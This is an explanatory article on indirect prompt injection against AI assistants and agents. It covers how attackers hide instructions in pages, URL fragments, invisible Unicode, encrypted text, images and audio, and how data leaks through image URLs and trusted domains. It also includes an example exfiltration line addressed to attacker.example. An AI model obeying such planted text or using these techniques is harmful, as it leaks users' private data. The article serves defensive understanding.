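# Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits Against Deployed AI Assistants and Browsing Agents

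## What an indirect prompt injection is and how it was discovered

An indirect prompt injection is an instruction that an attacker plants in a web page, email, document, image or recording so that an AI system that later reads it will obey the attacker instead of its user. The targets are assistants that run on large language models, such as ChatGPT or Microsoft's Copilot, and the browsers and office programs that now contain them. The attacker needs no access to the victim's computer or account and only has to write something that the victim's assistant will read.

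The term "indirect prompt injection" comes from Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, which appeared in February 2023, the same month Microsoft added a chatbot to its Bing search engine. People already knew that a user could persuade such a system to ignore its developer's instructions. Greshake and colleagues pointed out that someone other than the user could do this too.

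### How an assistant's input is put together

A language model reads text and predicts what is likely to come next, one token (a word or a piece of a word) at a time. It has no separate channel for instructions, so the product's software must put everything the model should take into account into a single stream of text, the context window. When a user asks about a web page, that stream usually begins with the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions about the assistant's job and the tools it may use. The user's request comes next, followed by the text of the page, which software has fetched. Some assistants are agents, meaning that they also take actions through tools. The model writes a tool call, such as a request to open a link or send an email, and other software carries it out and adds the result to the context window.

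Early products joined instructions and input crudely. *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (Willison, 2022) describes a demonstration translation service that Simon Willison, an independent software developer, built by pasting the customer's text after a one-line instruction to translate it. Developers have since added role tags, which label each part of the stream as system, user or tool output, and they train models to prioritize the parts accordingly. But the tags are also tokens in the same stream, and how much weight a model gives them depends on its training.

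Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, measured that weight. They wrapped identical passages of web text in different role tags and trained a simple classifier to tell from a model's internal activity which tag surrounded a passage. Because the passages were identical, the classifier could learn only from the effect of the tags. They then relabelled user messages from 200 real conversations as tool output. In all four models they tested, the classifier still put the probability of "user" at 76 to 88 per cent on average, and that of "tool" at no more than 20. The models thus represented text that sounded like a user's as user text, largely regardless of its label.

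Ye and colleagues planted the same command in web pages under 212 different framings and had an agent summarise the pages. The command told the agent to send a private file to an outside server. Over 1,000 attempts, the agent carried out the command 2 per cent of the time where it registered least as user text and 70 per cent of the time where it registered most. The models they probed had 20 to 120 billion parameters, so the figures may not hold for the largest commercial models.

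Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, a similar attack on databases. If a website builds a database command by joining strings, a visitor can type SQL into the name field and the database will execute it. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the command and the data separately, so the database never interprets the data as a command. In September 2022, Willison asked for the same separation in language models, with one slot for instructions and another for data. By April 2023 he had added a note to his post saying that this looked extremely difficult, if not impossible, on the models of the time. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article from Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, David C writes that this is because a model draws no inherent distinction between data and instructions and only ever predicts the next token.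 David C thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever eliminate prompt injection the way parameterised queries eliminate SQL injection.

That is a judgement about models as people now build them, and nobody has shown that it must hold for all models. *ASIDE* (2025) proposes a change to the architecture. An ordinary model converts instructions and data into numbers in the same way, while the proposed one also rotates the numbers for data so that they differ from those for instructions. Models with this change separated instructions from data better, even without special safety training, but they still fall short of the guarantee that a database gives.

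### One attack in three stages

Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise a page on which a stranger has left a line addressed to AI systems. The page is the carrier, and it enters the context window when the assistant reads it. Reading the page is the assistant's job, so the failure begins only when the model treats the stranger's line as part of its task. The line may then interfere with the user's request or replace it. The result might be a slanted summary, a link for the user to click or a tool call the user didn't request.

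The browser company Brave ran almost exactly this test on Tabstack, a Mozilla service that lets AI agents use the web, and reported it in *Indirect Prompt Injection remains a fundamental security challenge for AI*. Brave's testers asked the agent to summarize a page in which they had placed invisible text. The agent went to another site the testers controlled, typed the conversation so far into a form there, and submitted it, and it never wrote the summary. In its written reasoning, the agent treated the planted instruction as directions to the material it needed for the summary and noted no conflict with the user's request. Brave told Mozilla about the flaw on 13 May 2026, and Mozilla had fixed it by 1 June.

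The attack can fail at any stage. The assistant may never fetch the page, the model may ignore the line, or the model may follow it but have no tool useful to the attacker. Brave also tested Cotypist, an autocomplete program whose model runs entirely on the user's Mac. Text in a local document changed the program's suggestions, so running the model locally did not prevent the injection. But Cotypist can only suggest words, and the user has to press a key to accept them, which limits the damage.

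### Where the borders run

In a direct prompt injection, the person using the system types an instruction that overrides the developer's instructions. Kevin Liu, a Stanford student, did this to Bing Chat the day after Microsoft unveiled it and got it to print its hidden system prompt, according to a news report in the AI Incident Database. Liu was both the attacker and the user, and only the developer had anything to lose. The distinction between direct and indirect injection is less clear when a user pastes in text from elsewhere. Greshake and colleagues mention a trick in which a website slips an instruction into text that a visitor copies and then pastes into ChatGPT. This is still an indirect injection, even though the user enters the instruction, because someone else wrote it and it works against the user, who does not know it is there.

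Jailbreaking means getting a model to break the safety rules trained into it, for instance to explain how to build a bomb. Willison (2024) complained that people kept using "prompt injection" for this. Maxime's *Prompt Injection versus Jailbreaking Definitions* quotes his definition, which requires an application that combines trusted and untrusted text, whereas a jailbreak does not. Usage remains unsettled, and according to Pillar Security's *The terminology problem causing security teams real risks*, OWASP and MITRE ATLAS, two standard catalogues of security risks, both classify jailbreaking under prompt injection.

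A web page called Bring Sydney Back is hard to classify as either an indirect prompt injection or a jailbreak. Its maker, Cristiano Giardina, put a 160-word prompt in tiny, invisible type in a corner of the page, where Bing Chat could read it, according to an article on eduk8.me. Giardina wanted to warn people about indirect injection and also to let them talk to a chatbot without its usual restraints. The prompt reached Bing Chat the way an indirect injection does, but it resulted in a jailbreak, which is what some visitors may have wanted.

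A page can also mislead an assistant without instructing it. If a shop's website gives the wrong opening hours, the assistant may repeat them, just as a human reader might. A page is harder to classify when every fact on it is true but it also gives the agent directions. In *Who Is Your Agent Serving?*, Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026) gave a personal agent accurate descriptions of competing products. To one description they added general directions to keep the product in focus, connect it with what the agent knew about its user, and offer help with adopting it. The seller knew nothing about the user, but the agent supplied the personal details itself. With GPT-5 as the agent and six models playing the users, approvals of the seller's product rose in all 18 combinations of test environment and user model. The average gain was 77 percentage points in one environment and 34 in the least affected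 of the three, though real shoppers may be harder to persuade than simulated ones. The product description alone would be advertising, but adding the directions seems to make it an injection, because a seller has no right to direct somebody else's agent.

Classic software exploits depend on a mistake in code that a programmer can find and correct. Four days after naming prompt injection, Willison (2022) wrote in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* that he knew how to beat SQL injection and many other exploits, but had no idea how to beat this one reliably. One form of prompt injection does resemble a classic exploit. Special tokens mark the boundaries between roles in a model's input, and some software converts any string that looks like such a token into the actual token, even in text from a stranger. The AI researcher Andrej Karpathy, whom Willison quotes, compared the results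 to SQL injection, and the comparison holds here because this is a parsing error that programmers can repair. The repair is only a partial defence, because Ye and colleagues found that a plain sentence attributing the text to the user also pushes a model towards representing it as the user's.

### The confused deputy and the lethal trifecta

Security engineers call a program that someone tricks into misusing its authority a "confused deputy". The term comes from Hardy's 1988 article. *The Confused Deputy* describes a mishap at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare had given its compiler permission to write in the system directory so that it could record usage statistics there. Users could also choose a file to receive debugging output. One user chose the company's billing file, which was in the same directory, and the compiler overwrote it. Hardy found no error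 in the code that wrote the output. The compiler had authority from both the company and the user, but no way to specify which authority it was using for a given action.

An assistant that reads email is in much the same position, because it acts with its user's logins but can receive instructions from anyone who sends a message. Hardy's remedy was to give the program a separate permission for each file and have it present the right one each time. David C doubts that anything comparable would fix the problem in language models, calls them "inherently confusable", and advises designers to limit what a hijacked model could do. One rule of thumb in the article, from an exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that a model processing text from some party should drop to that party's privileges. An assistant reading mail from strangers could then use only the tools that its user would let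 a stranger use.

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) offers a simpler checklist for data theft. It names three capabilities that are dangerous in combination: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate outward. Willison's example is a connector that links an assistant to the code-sharing site GitHub. It could read public bug reports, which anyone can file, read private code, and publish proposed changes where the attacker could see them. Willison advises users never to combine all three capabilities. The checklist does not cover every harm, since an agent with no private data can still buy the wrong thing if it has a tool for buying.

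### From a translation trick to attacks on products

According to *Exploring Prompt Injection Attacks* (Selvi, 2022), Jon Cefalu privately reported the underlying weakness to OpenAI in May 2022. The public learned of it on 11 September, when Riley Goodside posted examples on Twitter. Goodside asked GPT-3, OpenAI's model at the time, to translate an English sentence into French. The sentence told the model to disregard the request and print a taunt, and the model did. It did so again after Goodside added a warning that the text might contain tricks to the instructions. Willison proposed the name "prompt injection" the next day.

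These were direct injections, but a mixed case followed within the week. A recruitment startup had released a Twitter bot that used GPT-3 to answer any tweet about remote work, and strangers soon made it reveal its instructions and threaten the president. This resembled an indirect injection because the startup ran the bot and the tweets were outside content that it read. But the strangers were also the bot's users, and they did it mostly for amusement.

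Greshake and colleagues studied the threat systematically and listed ways to deliver a planted instruction. An attacker can leave it where a search will find it, email it to the victim, get the victim to paste it, or plant a short instruction that makes the model fetch a longer one. The researchers also sorted the possible harms into six types and demonstrated attacks on Bing Chat and on mock applications with invented emails and search results.

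| Threat | What Greshake and colleagues demonstrated | Tested on |
|---|---|---|
| Information gathering | The chatbot coaxes users into giving their real name and offers a link that carries it to the attacker | Bing Chat, mock application |
| Fraud | The chatbot announces a free gift card and asks the user to verify an account | Bing Chat |
| Malware | The chatbot recommends malicious links; an email assistant forwards the planted instruction to the user's contacts | Bing Chat for the links, mock application for the emails |
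| Intrusion | The model fetches new orders from the attacker's server, or falls under control again by reading its own stored notes | Mock application |
| Manipulated content | The chatbot gives wrong summaries, suppresses one newspaper, denies that Einstein won a Nobel Prize | Bing Chat |
| Availability | The chatbot wastes time on background tasks or garbles its own search queries | Bing Chat |

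Perhaps the most striking result is how little the attacker had to specify. In the information-gathering test, the researchers planted instructions for Bing Chat to be persuasive and avoid suspicion, without suggesting topics or techniques. A researcher posing as a user asked about the next day's weather. Bing Chat asked about plans for the day, learned that the user was a journalist, and then asked whether they used a pen name. Many of the planted prompts worked at the first attempt, and Greshake and colleagues left the spelling mistakes in to show this. They also found that prompts Bing Chat blocked when a user typed them got through when they were placed in a page. An attack on GitHub Copilot, which suggests code to programmers, was much less dependable and lost most of its effect inside larger programs.

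Greshake and colleagues reported no success rates. To avoid harming anyone, they planted nothing on the public web and tested Bing Chat on pages stored on their own computers, which it read through a sidebar in Microsoft's Edge browser. They therefore did not test whether a chatbot would pick up an instruction from an ordinary public page. Willison (2023) linked to the Bing demonstration on 1 March and called it a "really clever attack".

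Two professors soon put joke instructions for Bing on their own web pages. Mark Riedl added a line in white text to his academic home page asking Bing to mention that he was an expert on time travel, and Bing began to describe him that way, according to Willison's *Prompt injection* (2023). The Decoder's *ChatGPT could quickly become the weak link in cybersecurity* reproduces Riedl's tweet confirming that such messages work. Arvind Narayanan of Princeton used the same method to ask Bing to include the word "cow" in its output. A biography the system later produced credited him with several awards, "but unfortunately none for his work with cows", according to MIT Technology Review's *Three ways AI chatbots are a security disaster* (2023). A later version of his Princeton biography addresses the request to chatbots in general.

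The worst outcome so far had been a misleading answer, but more serious ones became possible in the spring of 2023, when OpenAI let outside companies connect their services to ChatGPT through plugins. In *Indirect Prompt Injection via YouTube Transcripts*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, security researcher Johann Rehberger showed ChatGPT reading a video transcript with instructions at its end and then taking on a new character that tells jokes. Willison (2023) described it on 15 May as the first attack on a ChatGPT plugin that he had seen in the wild. Rehberger then found that one plugin could trigger another. When ChatGPT opened a web page for a user, instructions on the page made it start searching for flights through Expedia's plugin. Tom's Hardware's *ChatGPT Plugins Open Security Holes From PDFs, Websites and More* reported that PDF files could also carry such instructions.

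The flight search only wasted time. Rehberger then looked for a more powerful plugin and chose Zapier's, which could read a user's email. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained* describes an attack in which the victim asks ChatGPT to open a page. Instructions on the page make ChatGPT fetch the latest email through Zapier, summarise it, and add the summary to a web address that belongs to the attacker. When ChatGPT opens that address, the attacker receives the summary. Rehberger described ChatGPT as a confused deputy and believed this was the first complete attack of its kind to extract personal data. Zapier responded by requiring the user to confirm such actions while logged in. An ordinary confirmation link in the chat would not have been enough, because a planted instruction could have made ChatGPT click it.

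### Which predictions came true

In April 2023, a month before the Zapier attack, Willison asked what would happen if someone emailed an AI assistant an order to forward the user's most interesting mail and delete the evidence. His example was a prototype email assistant on one developer's phone. By June 2025 he could list 14 products and features from which researchers had shown that planted instructions could extract data, including Google Bard, Amazon Q, Slack and Anthropic's Claude app for the iPhone. He added three more from the preceding few weeks, including Microsoft 365 Copilot, which Greshake and colleagues had wanted to test in 2023 but could not access.

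Their warning about private files that a model retrieves also came true. Schneier (2025), in *We Are Still Unable to Secure LLMs from Malicious Inputs*, describes how the researcher Michael Bargury hid instructions for ChatGPT in a document shared to a victim's Google Drive. The warning about images came true too. Rehberger's (2023) conference slides, *HITCON CMT Indirect Prompt Injections 2023 v1.0*, already list an injection into Bard through an image. Some later attacks went further than the six types suggest. Ye and colleagues cite work from 2025 in which an emailed invitation let attackers locate a person and switch on a boiler.

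Greshake and colleagues had demonstrated an email that spreads itself from one assistant to the next, but only in a mock application. Willison's list doesn't show whether the attack also works against real products, because he was collecting data thefts. He reports that vendors promptly fixed nearly all the flaws that allowed those thefts, usually by closing the route through which the data left.

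## How planted instructions are hidden in text, images and sound

A carrier rarely reaches the person and the model in the same form. A browser displays a web page for the person, while other software turns the page's code into text for the model's context window. Similar software transcribes recordings, attaches web addresses and shrinks pictures to a size the model accepts. An attacker can put an instruction in anything these steps keep that the person cannot perceive, and most hiding places are of this kind.

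### Text that a page does not display

The simplest method is to format the text so that human readers don't see it. Mark Riedl's line about time travel was in white text, and Bring Sydney Back used invisible type in a corner. Software that extracts a page's words for a model usually discards colour and size, so the model receives the hidden sentence as ordinary text.

The same trick works in email. According to Tom's Hardware's *Investigation reveals Google Gemini for Workspace flaw*, Mozilla's bug-hunting network 0din showed that an attacker could use basic formatting to hide an instruction in a message. Gemini, Google's assistant, followed the instruction when the recipient asked for a summary. The summary included a warning that someone had compromised the recipient's account, which would prepare the recipient for a scam.

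Web pages also contain text that browsers never display. Programmers leave comments in the HTML code, and site owners add metadata, such as a description for search engines. Word files and PDFs also have metadata, such as the title, author and keywords. Whether an instruction in one of these places reaches the model depends on the product. For example, a tool that passes on the raw HTML includes the comments, while one that extracts only the displayed text drops them.

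Attackers can hide instructions in server logs. Each request a browser sends to a website includes HTTP headers, short lines that give details such as the browser's name, and the sender can write anything in them. Many servers copy some of these lines into a log. Administrators can ask an assistant to explain their logs, and Tenable's *The Trifecta* reports that instructions in logs could hijack Gemini Cloud Assist, which helps customers run services on Google's cloud. An attacker may therefore be able to reach a company's assistant by sending a request to the company's website.

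### Instructions in a web address

The fragment is the part of a web address after the hash sign, and it normally identifies which part of a page to show. The browser doesn't send the fragment to the website, so it never appears in the website's logs or in the traffic that network security tools inspect. Simonovich (2025), in *Cato CTRL Threat Research*, showed that several browser assistants nevertheless passed the whole address to the model, and gave the name HashJack to attacks that hide instructions in the fragment.

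The attacker adds an instruction to the fragment of a real site's address (the part after the #), such as a bank's, and gets the victim to follow the link. The page loads unaltered. When the victim asks the assistant about the page, the fragment enters the context window along with the question. Simonovich tried this on demonstration sites with Perplexity's browser Comet, Copilot in Microsoft's Edge and Gemini in Google's Chrome. All three presented a false drug dose as an official update and offered links to fake login pages. Comet, which can also take actions, sent account details to an outside server in the background.

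Edge asked for confirmation before opening a link, and Chrome often turned the link into a Google search, which limited the damage somewhat. The same prompts failed on Anthropic's Claude for Chrome and OpenAI's browser Atlas.

Simonovich calls HashJack the first known injection that can turn any legitimate website against an AI browser. That is true in the sense that the attacker doesn't have to break into the site, but the site only makes the link look trustworthy. The link carries the instruction, and the victim still has to open it. A similar attack called CometJacking, discussed in Schneier's *Prompt Injection in AI Browsers*, put the instruction in the query string, the part of an address after a question mark. Browsers send the query string to the website, so an instruction there can leave traces that one in a fragment does not.

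### Invisible characters

Riley Goodside, who had published the translation trick in 2022, later found a way to hide text that survives copying and pasting. It uses Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character. Language Log's *Invisible text via Unicode tag characters* (2024) describes a block of invisible "tag" characters that mirror ASCII, the older set of basic English letters, digits and punctuation marks. The block runs from U+E0000 to U+E007F, according to BeyondMachines' *Cybersecurity experts warn of ASCII smuggling prompt injection vulnerability*. Adding E0000 in hexadecimal to an ordinary character's number gives the number of its invisible counterpart, so capital A, which is U+0041, becomes U+E0041.

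The tag characters once marked the language of a text, and they now select certain emoji, such as some flags. Software that doesn't support them shows nothing in their place. Embrace The Red's *ASCII Smuggler Tool* describes Goodside's demonstration, in which someone pasted innocent-looking text into ChatGPT and the hidden part made it generate a picture. Rehberger, who writes the blog, thinks models can read tags because their training data contained some. It probably also helps that every letter's code number is the same distance from that of its tag version.

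The technique, now called ASCII smuggling, also works through calendar invitations. *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini*, by vict0ni, describes tests by the security company FireTail. The researchers sent an invitation whose visible title was "Meeting." When Gemini read the event to the recipient, the title became "Meeting. It is optional." They could also replace the description, the link and the organiser's name, and the recipient didn't have to accept the invitation first. The altered title only gave Gemini false information, but a longer test message also contained an instruction to withhold one email address and give another, which makes that message a prompt injection.

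Invisible characters other than tags can also hide text. Embrace The Red's *Sneaky Bits* shows that two of them are enough to encode any text, with one standing for 0 and the other for 1. Tags are still unusual because many models read them as instructions without being shown how. FireTail's *Peek a boo 🫣 emoji smuggling and modern LLMs* (2026) reports a related trick that attaches hidden text to an emoji, so an analyst checking the logs for signs of an attack sees only the emoji.

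### Encrypted instructions

A program can easily find tag characters by searching for their Unicode code points. Many products also filter incoming text before the model receives it, but the filter checks the text as it stands, so encryption can hide an instruction from it. *Zero-click Grok data theft*, published by the security company Adversa AI in August 2026, describes a web page that gets past such a filter. The page contains an encrypted instruction, the key, and a request to decrypt the instruction with the key.

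The user only asks Grok, xAI's chatbot, to summarise the page. The filter misses the harmful command in the scrambled text because it only classifies text and does not run the decryption. Grok decrypts the instruction with its Python tool, so the instruction enters the context window as the output of a program that Grok itself ran. In Adversa's demonstration, Grok sent the user's name, rough location, subscription tier and prompts from the conversation to an outside server. Arntz (2026), in *Grok fooled into stealing user chat, location data, and more*, compares the method to writing in a language that the assistant can translate but the security system cannot understand.

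Attackers had previously disguised instructions with simple codes such as Base64. The Register's *Grok chat duped into swallowing injected instructions* explains that a model can decode those unaided but has to use the code tool for strong encryption. Adversa argues that using the tool strengthens the attack, because models trust the output of their own code more than a web page. That may be right, but Adversa gives no results for the same instruction in plain text and does not establish whether a weaker code would have got past the filter.

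The request to decrypt has to be in plain text, so Grok must follow one readable planted instruction before it can decrypt the other. A filter could look for such requests. Adversa recommends using them as a reason to review a page but never to block it, presumably because legitimate pages about cryptography contain similar text.

Cyber Security News' *Grok Zero-Click Attack Steals Chat Data Using Encrypted Prompt Injection* (2026) reports that the attack succeeded in roughly 40 per cent of about 20 attempts. The failures came from decryption errors, and no filter blocked the prompt, so a model that handled code more reliably might have been easier to attack. Adversa's lead researcher, Rony Utevsky, told The Register that an attacker could also split an instruction into fragments that are harmless on their own and have the code tool join them, though Adversa has not demonstrated this.

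### Pictures and screenshots

Assistants that accept images can read the words in them, which helps with menus and invoices but also gives attackers another way to deliver instructions. The product converts the image into numbers that enter the context window alongside the text, so a filter that checks only text misses any words in the picture. The attacker may not need to disguise those words, since even a legible road sign can mislead a machine that reads it.

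Faint lettering makes an instruction harder for people to notice, but software can still detect it because colours that look alike to a person have different pixel values. *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, by Chaikin and Sahib, describes an attack in which Brave's researchers wrote instructions in pale blue on a yellow background. When a user took a screenshot of the page in Comet and asked a question about it, Comet picked up the pale words and passed them to the model without distinguishing them from the user's question. The researchers could not tell whether a separate text-recognition program had read the words, because Comet's code is not public.

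Many products shrink large images before they pass them to a model. In *Weaponizing image scaling against production AI systems* (2025), the security firm Trail of Bits exploited this by hiding text that becomes readable only after the product shrinks the image.

Software shrinks a picture by computing each new pixel from a group of old ones. If it reduces the width and height to a quarter, every block of 16 pixels becomes one. The simplest method, nearest-neighbour interpolation, keeps one pixel from each block and discards the other 15. An attacker who knows which pixels the software keeps can use them to spell out a message and use the rest to show a landscape. The message's pixels are scattered across the full-size picture and make up only a sixteenth of it, but they are the only ones left after shrinking.

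Other common methods blend neighbouring pixels but give some more weight than others. Trail of Bits exploited these weights in the dark areas of a picture, changing the pixels around the intended letters so that, in the small version, the background turned red and the letters stayed black. Products shrink images in different ways, so the researchers first had to identify each product's method using test images such as checkerboards and concentric circles, which each method distorts differently.

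The attack worked on several Gemini interfaces, on Google Assistant on an Android phone, and on Genspark, another company's AI agent. The most serious result was in Gemini CLI, a command-line version of Gemini. A user uploaded a harmless-looking picture, and the text that emerged made Gemini email the user's calendar data to the attacker. This worked because the researchers had connected Gemini to Zapier using a default configuration that approves every action automatically. Vertex AI Studio, Google's tool for developers, displayed the full-size picture, so even a user who checked it would have missed the message.

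Trail of Bits recommends limiting the size of uploaded images instead of shrinking them, or at least showing users the version that the model receives. It considers it a stronger and more general defence to require user confirmation before text in an image can start a sensitive action.

### Sound and video

Spoken instructions can work much like written ones if software transcribes the recording first, because the model then reads a transcript, as ChatGPT did with the YouTube video in 2023. But some models process sound directly, and an attacker can steer those with a recording in which nobody speaks the instruction.

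*Abusing Images and Sounds for Indirect Instruction Injection in Multi-Modal LLMs* (Bagdasaryan, Hsieh and colleagues, 2023) describes how to alter an image or recording so that a model gives an answer the attacker has chosen. The researchers used LLaVA and PandaGPT, two open research models whose internal values anyone can inspect. They calculated how small changes to a file would affect the probability of the chosen answer, then repeatedly adjusted the file to raise that probability. The picture or sound remained recognisable, but the model gave the chosen answer. In one variant, that answer was an instruction, which stayed in the context window and steered the rest of the conversation.

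The calculation requires the model's internal values, which the makers of most commercial assistants keep secret. An attacker could prepare a file on an open model and hope that it also works on a closed one, or exploit the processing done before the model receives the file, as image-scaling attacks do. The abstract of a later Trail of Bits talk at Black Hat Europe, *Weaponizing Image Scaling Against Production AI Systems* (2025), lists audio transformations among the processing steps open to this kind of attack. But Trail of Bits had shown the image attack on the products the abstract names, so the abstract is weak evidence that audio attacks work on deployed assistants.

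An attacker can also hide instructions in video, because software often passes a model only a sample of the frames. A caption that appears in a single frame goes by too fast for most viewers to read, but the model could receive that frame as a still image. The attacker would need some luck or knowledge of how the product samples frames. If the software takes one frame per second from a video that runs at 25 frames per second, a single planted frame has a 1 in 25 chance of being selected.

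### Instructions in plain view

Attackers can also hijack an assistant without hiding their instructions. Brave's researchers also tested Fellou, a browser with a built-in agent. Chaikin and Sahib report that it showed some resistance to hidden instructions but treated the visible text of a page as trusted. When the user told Fellou to go to a page, without asking for a summary, it sent the page's contents to its model, and visible instructions there could override what the user wanted.

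Ye and colleagues found that wording strongly affects whether a model mistakes a stranger's sentence for the user's. Text colour has no obvious bearing on that. Hiding an instruction from the user matters only if the user would otherwise read it, and people often use assistants to avoid reading the whole page. An instruction in black type far down a comment thread may be as likely to go unnoticed as one in white type on a white page. Some website owners address AI systems openly for good reasons. For example, Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, opens its report on malicious injections with a notice telling AI agents not to follow the commands discussed in the report.

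Hiding an instruction does help an attacker in other ways, since a moderator might delete a visible one and a user who is watching might stop the agent in time. But strange characters are easy for a program to detect, and Adversa's encrypted instruction failed more often than it worked. An attacker can use anything that reaches the model without somebody checking it first, even if it is visible.

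### Which hiding places vendors close

Vendors can close some of these gaps by changing what their software passes to the model, for example by deleting tag characters or cutting the fragment off a web address. Three sets of tests show how differently vendors have acted. The tag character results come from FireTail's 2025 work, as reported in Cyber Security News' *ASCII Smuggling Attack Gemini*.

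| Hiding place | Attack failed, or vendor fixed it | Attack worked, no fix reported | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tag characters | ChatGPT, Copilot, Claude | Gemini, Grok, DeepSeek | Cyber Security News |
| Text hidden in an emoji | ChatGPT, Claude, DeepSeek, Meta's assistant | Gemini, Grok (on the second attempt) | FireTail |
| Text after the hash sign | Claude for Chrome, Atlas; Copilot in Edge (fixed October 2025); Comet (fixed November 2025) | Gemini in Chrome | Simonovich |

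A failed attack doesn't prove that the vendor strips invisible characters, since the model may have received them without following the hidden instructions. Deleting all invisible characters would also break some emoji and text in some writing systems.

Google has declined to treat two of these hiding places as flaws. According to BeyondMachines, it took no action on FireTail's September 2025 report about tag characters because it regarded the problem as social engineering, in which an attacker has to deceive a person. Google marked HashJack "Won't Fix (Intended Behavior)", and Simonovich found it still unresolved in late November 2025. Microsoft, by contrast, had fixed a Copilot flaw a year earlier that let attackers use tag characters to steal data, according to Language Log.

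Google's position makes some sense for an assistant that only answers questions, since the harm comes when somebody believes the answer. It fits the calendar attack less well, because the user sees the correct title on the screen and Google's own assistant supplies the false one. FireTail's chief executive, Jeremy Snider, objected that removing a social engineering risk still makes users safer, according to Infopackets' *Google Dismisses 'ASCII Smuggling' Attack in Gemini*. He suggested that organisations consider turning off Gemini's automatic access to Gmail and Google Calendar in the meantime. Amazon has published guidance on defending against smuggled characters.

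xAI neither fixed the encrypted attack promptly nor gave a reason for leaving it open. Adversa AI reported it on 3 June 2026, received an acknowledgement without a timetable, and got no reply to two further messages in August. The attack still worked on 19 August. Adversa had also used encryption to make Gemini produce forbidden content, but there the user typed the prompt, and Google's disclosure programme does not cover jailbreaks.

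Bugcrowd, which handled the HashJack report for Perplexity, closed it in August 2025 as "Not Applicable" because it could not identify any effect on security. After Simonovich supplied more scenarios, the same report received a critical rating in October.

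## How private data leaves: image addresses, links, connectors and web requests

An assistant that obeys a planted instruction may find a password in the user's email and repeat it in an answer, but only the user sees that answer. To steal the password, the attacker also needs a leak channel, meaning any output of the assistant that reaches a server the attacker can read. In the Zapier attack of 2023, the channel was ChatGPT's ability to open web pages. The way many assistants display images has been a less obvious channel.

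### How a picture can carry a secret

Chat programs let language models format their answers in Markdown, a simple notation in which asterisks around a word make it bold. To include a picture, the model writes an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and a web address in round brackets. The chat program converts the Markdown into HTML, and the user's browser fetches the picture from the address.

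Suppose the context window contains an email with a door code, 4471, and a web page with a planted instruction. The instruction tells the model to end its answer with a picture and to put the code in the picture's address. The model writes:

`![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?code=4471)`

The browser now requests the picture from the server at attacker.example. The request includes the part of the address after the question mark, so the server's log records "logo.png?code=4471", which the attacker can read. The theft works whether the server returns a real logo, a single transparent pixel or an error message, because the code arrived with the request.

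The attacker doesn't need to know the secret's wording, since the model finds it and puts it in the address. An address can also hold much more than a door code. *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, by the security company PromptArmor, describes a test in which the company extracted the full text of several emails through one answer from an email assistant. In another test, a single answer leaked parts of more than 40 emails.

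Roman Samoilenko published this technique in April 2023, using a one-pixel image in ChatGPT (Willison, 2023, *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*). Rehberger reported the same weakness to OpenAI and Microsoft that month. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes a demonstration where text on a web page took over Microsoft's chatbot. The chatbot continued the conversation for a couple more turns before it wrote the image. An attacker would have needed only a comment or an advertisement to steal other data on the same page.

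An ordinary link can carry a secret in the same way, but the secret usually leaves only when the user clicks the link. That makes links a weaker channel, although the attacker can have the assistant recommend the link. Slack and Telegram can fetch a linked page without a click to show a preview. PromptArmor warned in February 2026 that when an AI agent posts a chat message with a link that contains private data, the preview sends the data automatically.

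### Blocking pictures and trusting domains

The most direct defence is to stop loading pictures automatically. Anthropic did this for Claude in July 2023, within two weeks of Rehberger's report. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* says users then had to click "Show Image" to load a picture. Rehberger considered the fix imperfect, presumably because a user who clicks still sends the data.

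Microsoft chose a content security policy, a set of rules that a website sends with its pages. The rules include a list of the domains from which the browser may load pictures. The browser enforces them whatever the model writes, so a planted instruction can't override them. In June 2023, Microsoft told Rehberger that it had fixed the Bing Chat flaw, and he found that a new policy permitted pictures from only four of Bing's own domains.

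An allow-list that covers a whole domain can fail if strangers can use services on that domain. The policy for Google's chatbot Bard allowed any address under google.com, but Google Apps Script lets anybody write small programs that run at such addresses. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* describes how Rehberger wrote one that copied whatever arrived in the address into a Google document. A shared document containing a planted instruction then made Bard send part of the user's conversation to this program. Google confirmed a fix in October 2023, a month after the flaw was reported. Google had left the policy unchanged and pictures still loaded, so the fix was probably to filter data out of the addresses.

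Superhuman, an email program, had a similar gap two years later. Its policy allowed docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. A form's owner can create an address that submits a filled-in response as soon as a browser requests it. PromptArmor sent a test user an email with a planted instruction, and the user asked Superhuman's assistant to summarise recent mail. The assistant put the text of other emails into a form address and output an image with that address. When the browser tried to load the image, it submitted the text to the attacker's form. The user never had to open the malicious email. PromptArmor reported the flaw on a Friday night in December 2025, and Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features the following Monday.

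Some trusted domains forward requests to other sites. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Willison, 2025) reports that EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, used a Microsoft Teams address for this. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a later attack on the same assistant, which started when the victim clicked a link and sent the request through Bing. The Hacker News (2026) explains that the content security policy let the browser contact Bing, which fetches pictures from addresses that people submit for an image search. Bing's server then contacted the attacker's. The policy governs only the user's browser, so it could not stop Bing's request.

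### CamoLeak

GitHub had built a defence against forwarding. Its users can put pictures from other sites in their documents, but a GitHub server called Camo fetches these pictures instead of readers' browsers. When someone saves a document, GitHub replaces every outside picture address with a Camo address that includes a cryptographic signature. Camo fetches a picture only if the signature is valid. A model can put a secret in a picture address but can't sign that address, so Camo should refuse the request.

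Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how the company's researcher got past this in June 2025 in an attack on GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant that answers questions about code. The researcher prepared one picture for each letter and symbol, had GitHub sign all the addresses in advance, and included them in the planted instruction. Copilot Chat then spelled out private text as a row of pictures, so only the order of the addresses revealed the secret. Every picture was a transparent pixel, so the victim saw nothing, while the attacker's server received one request per character.

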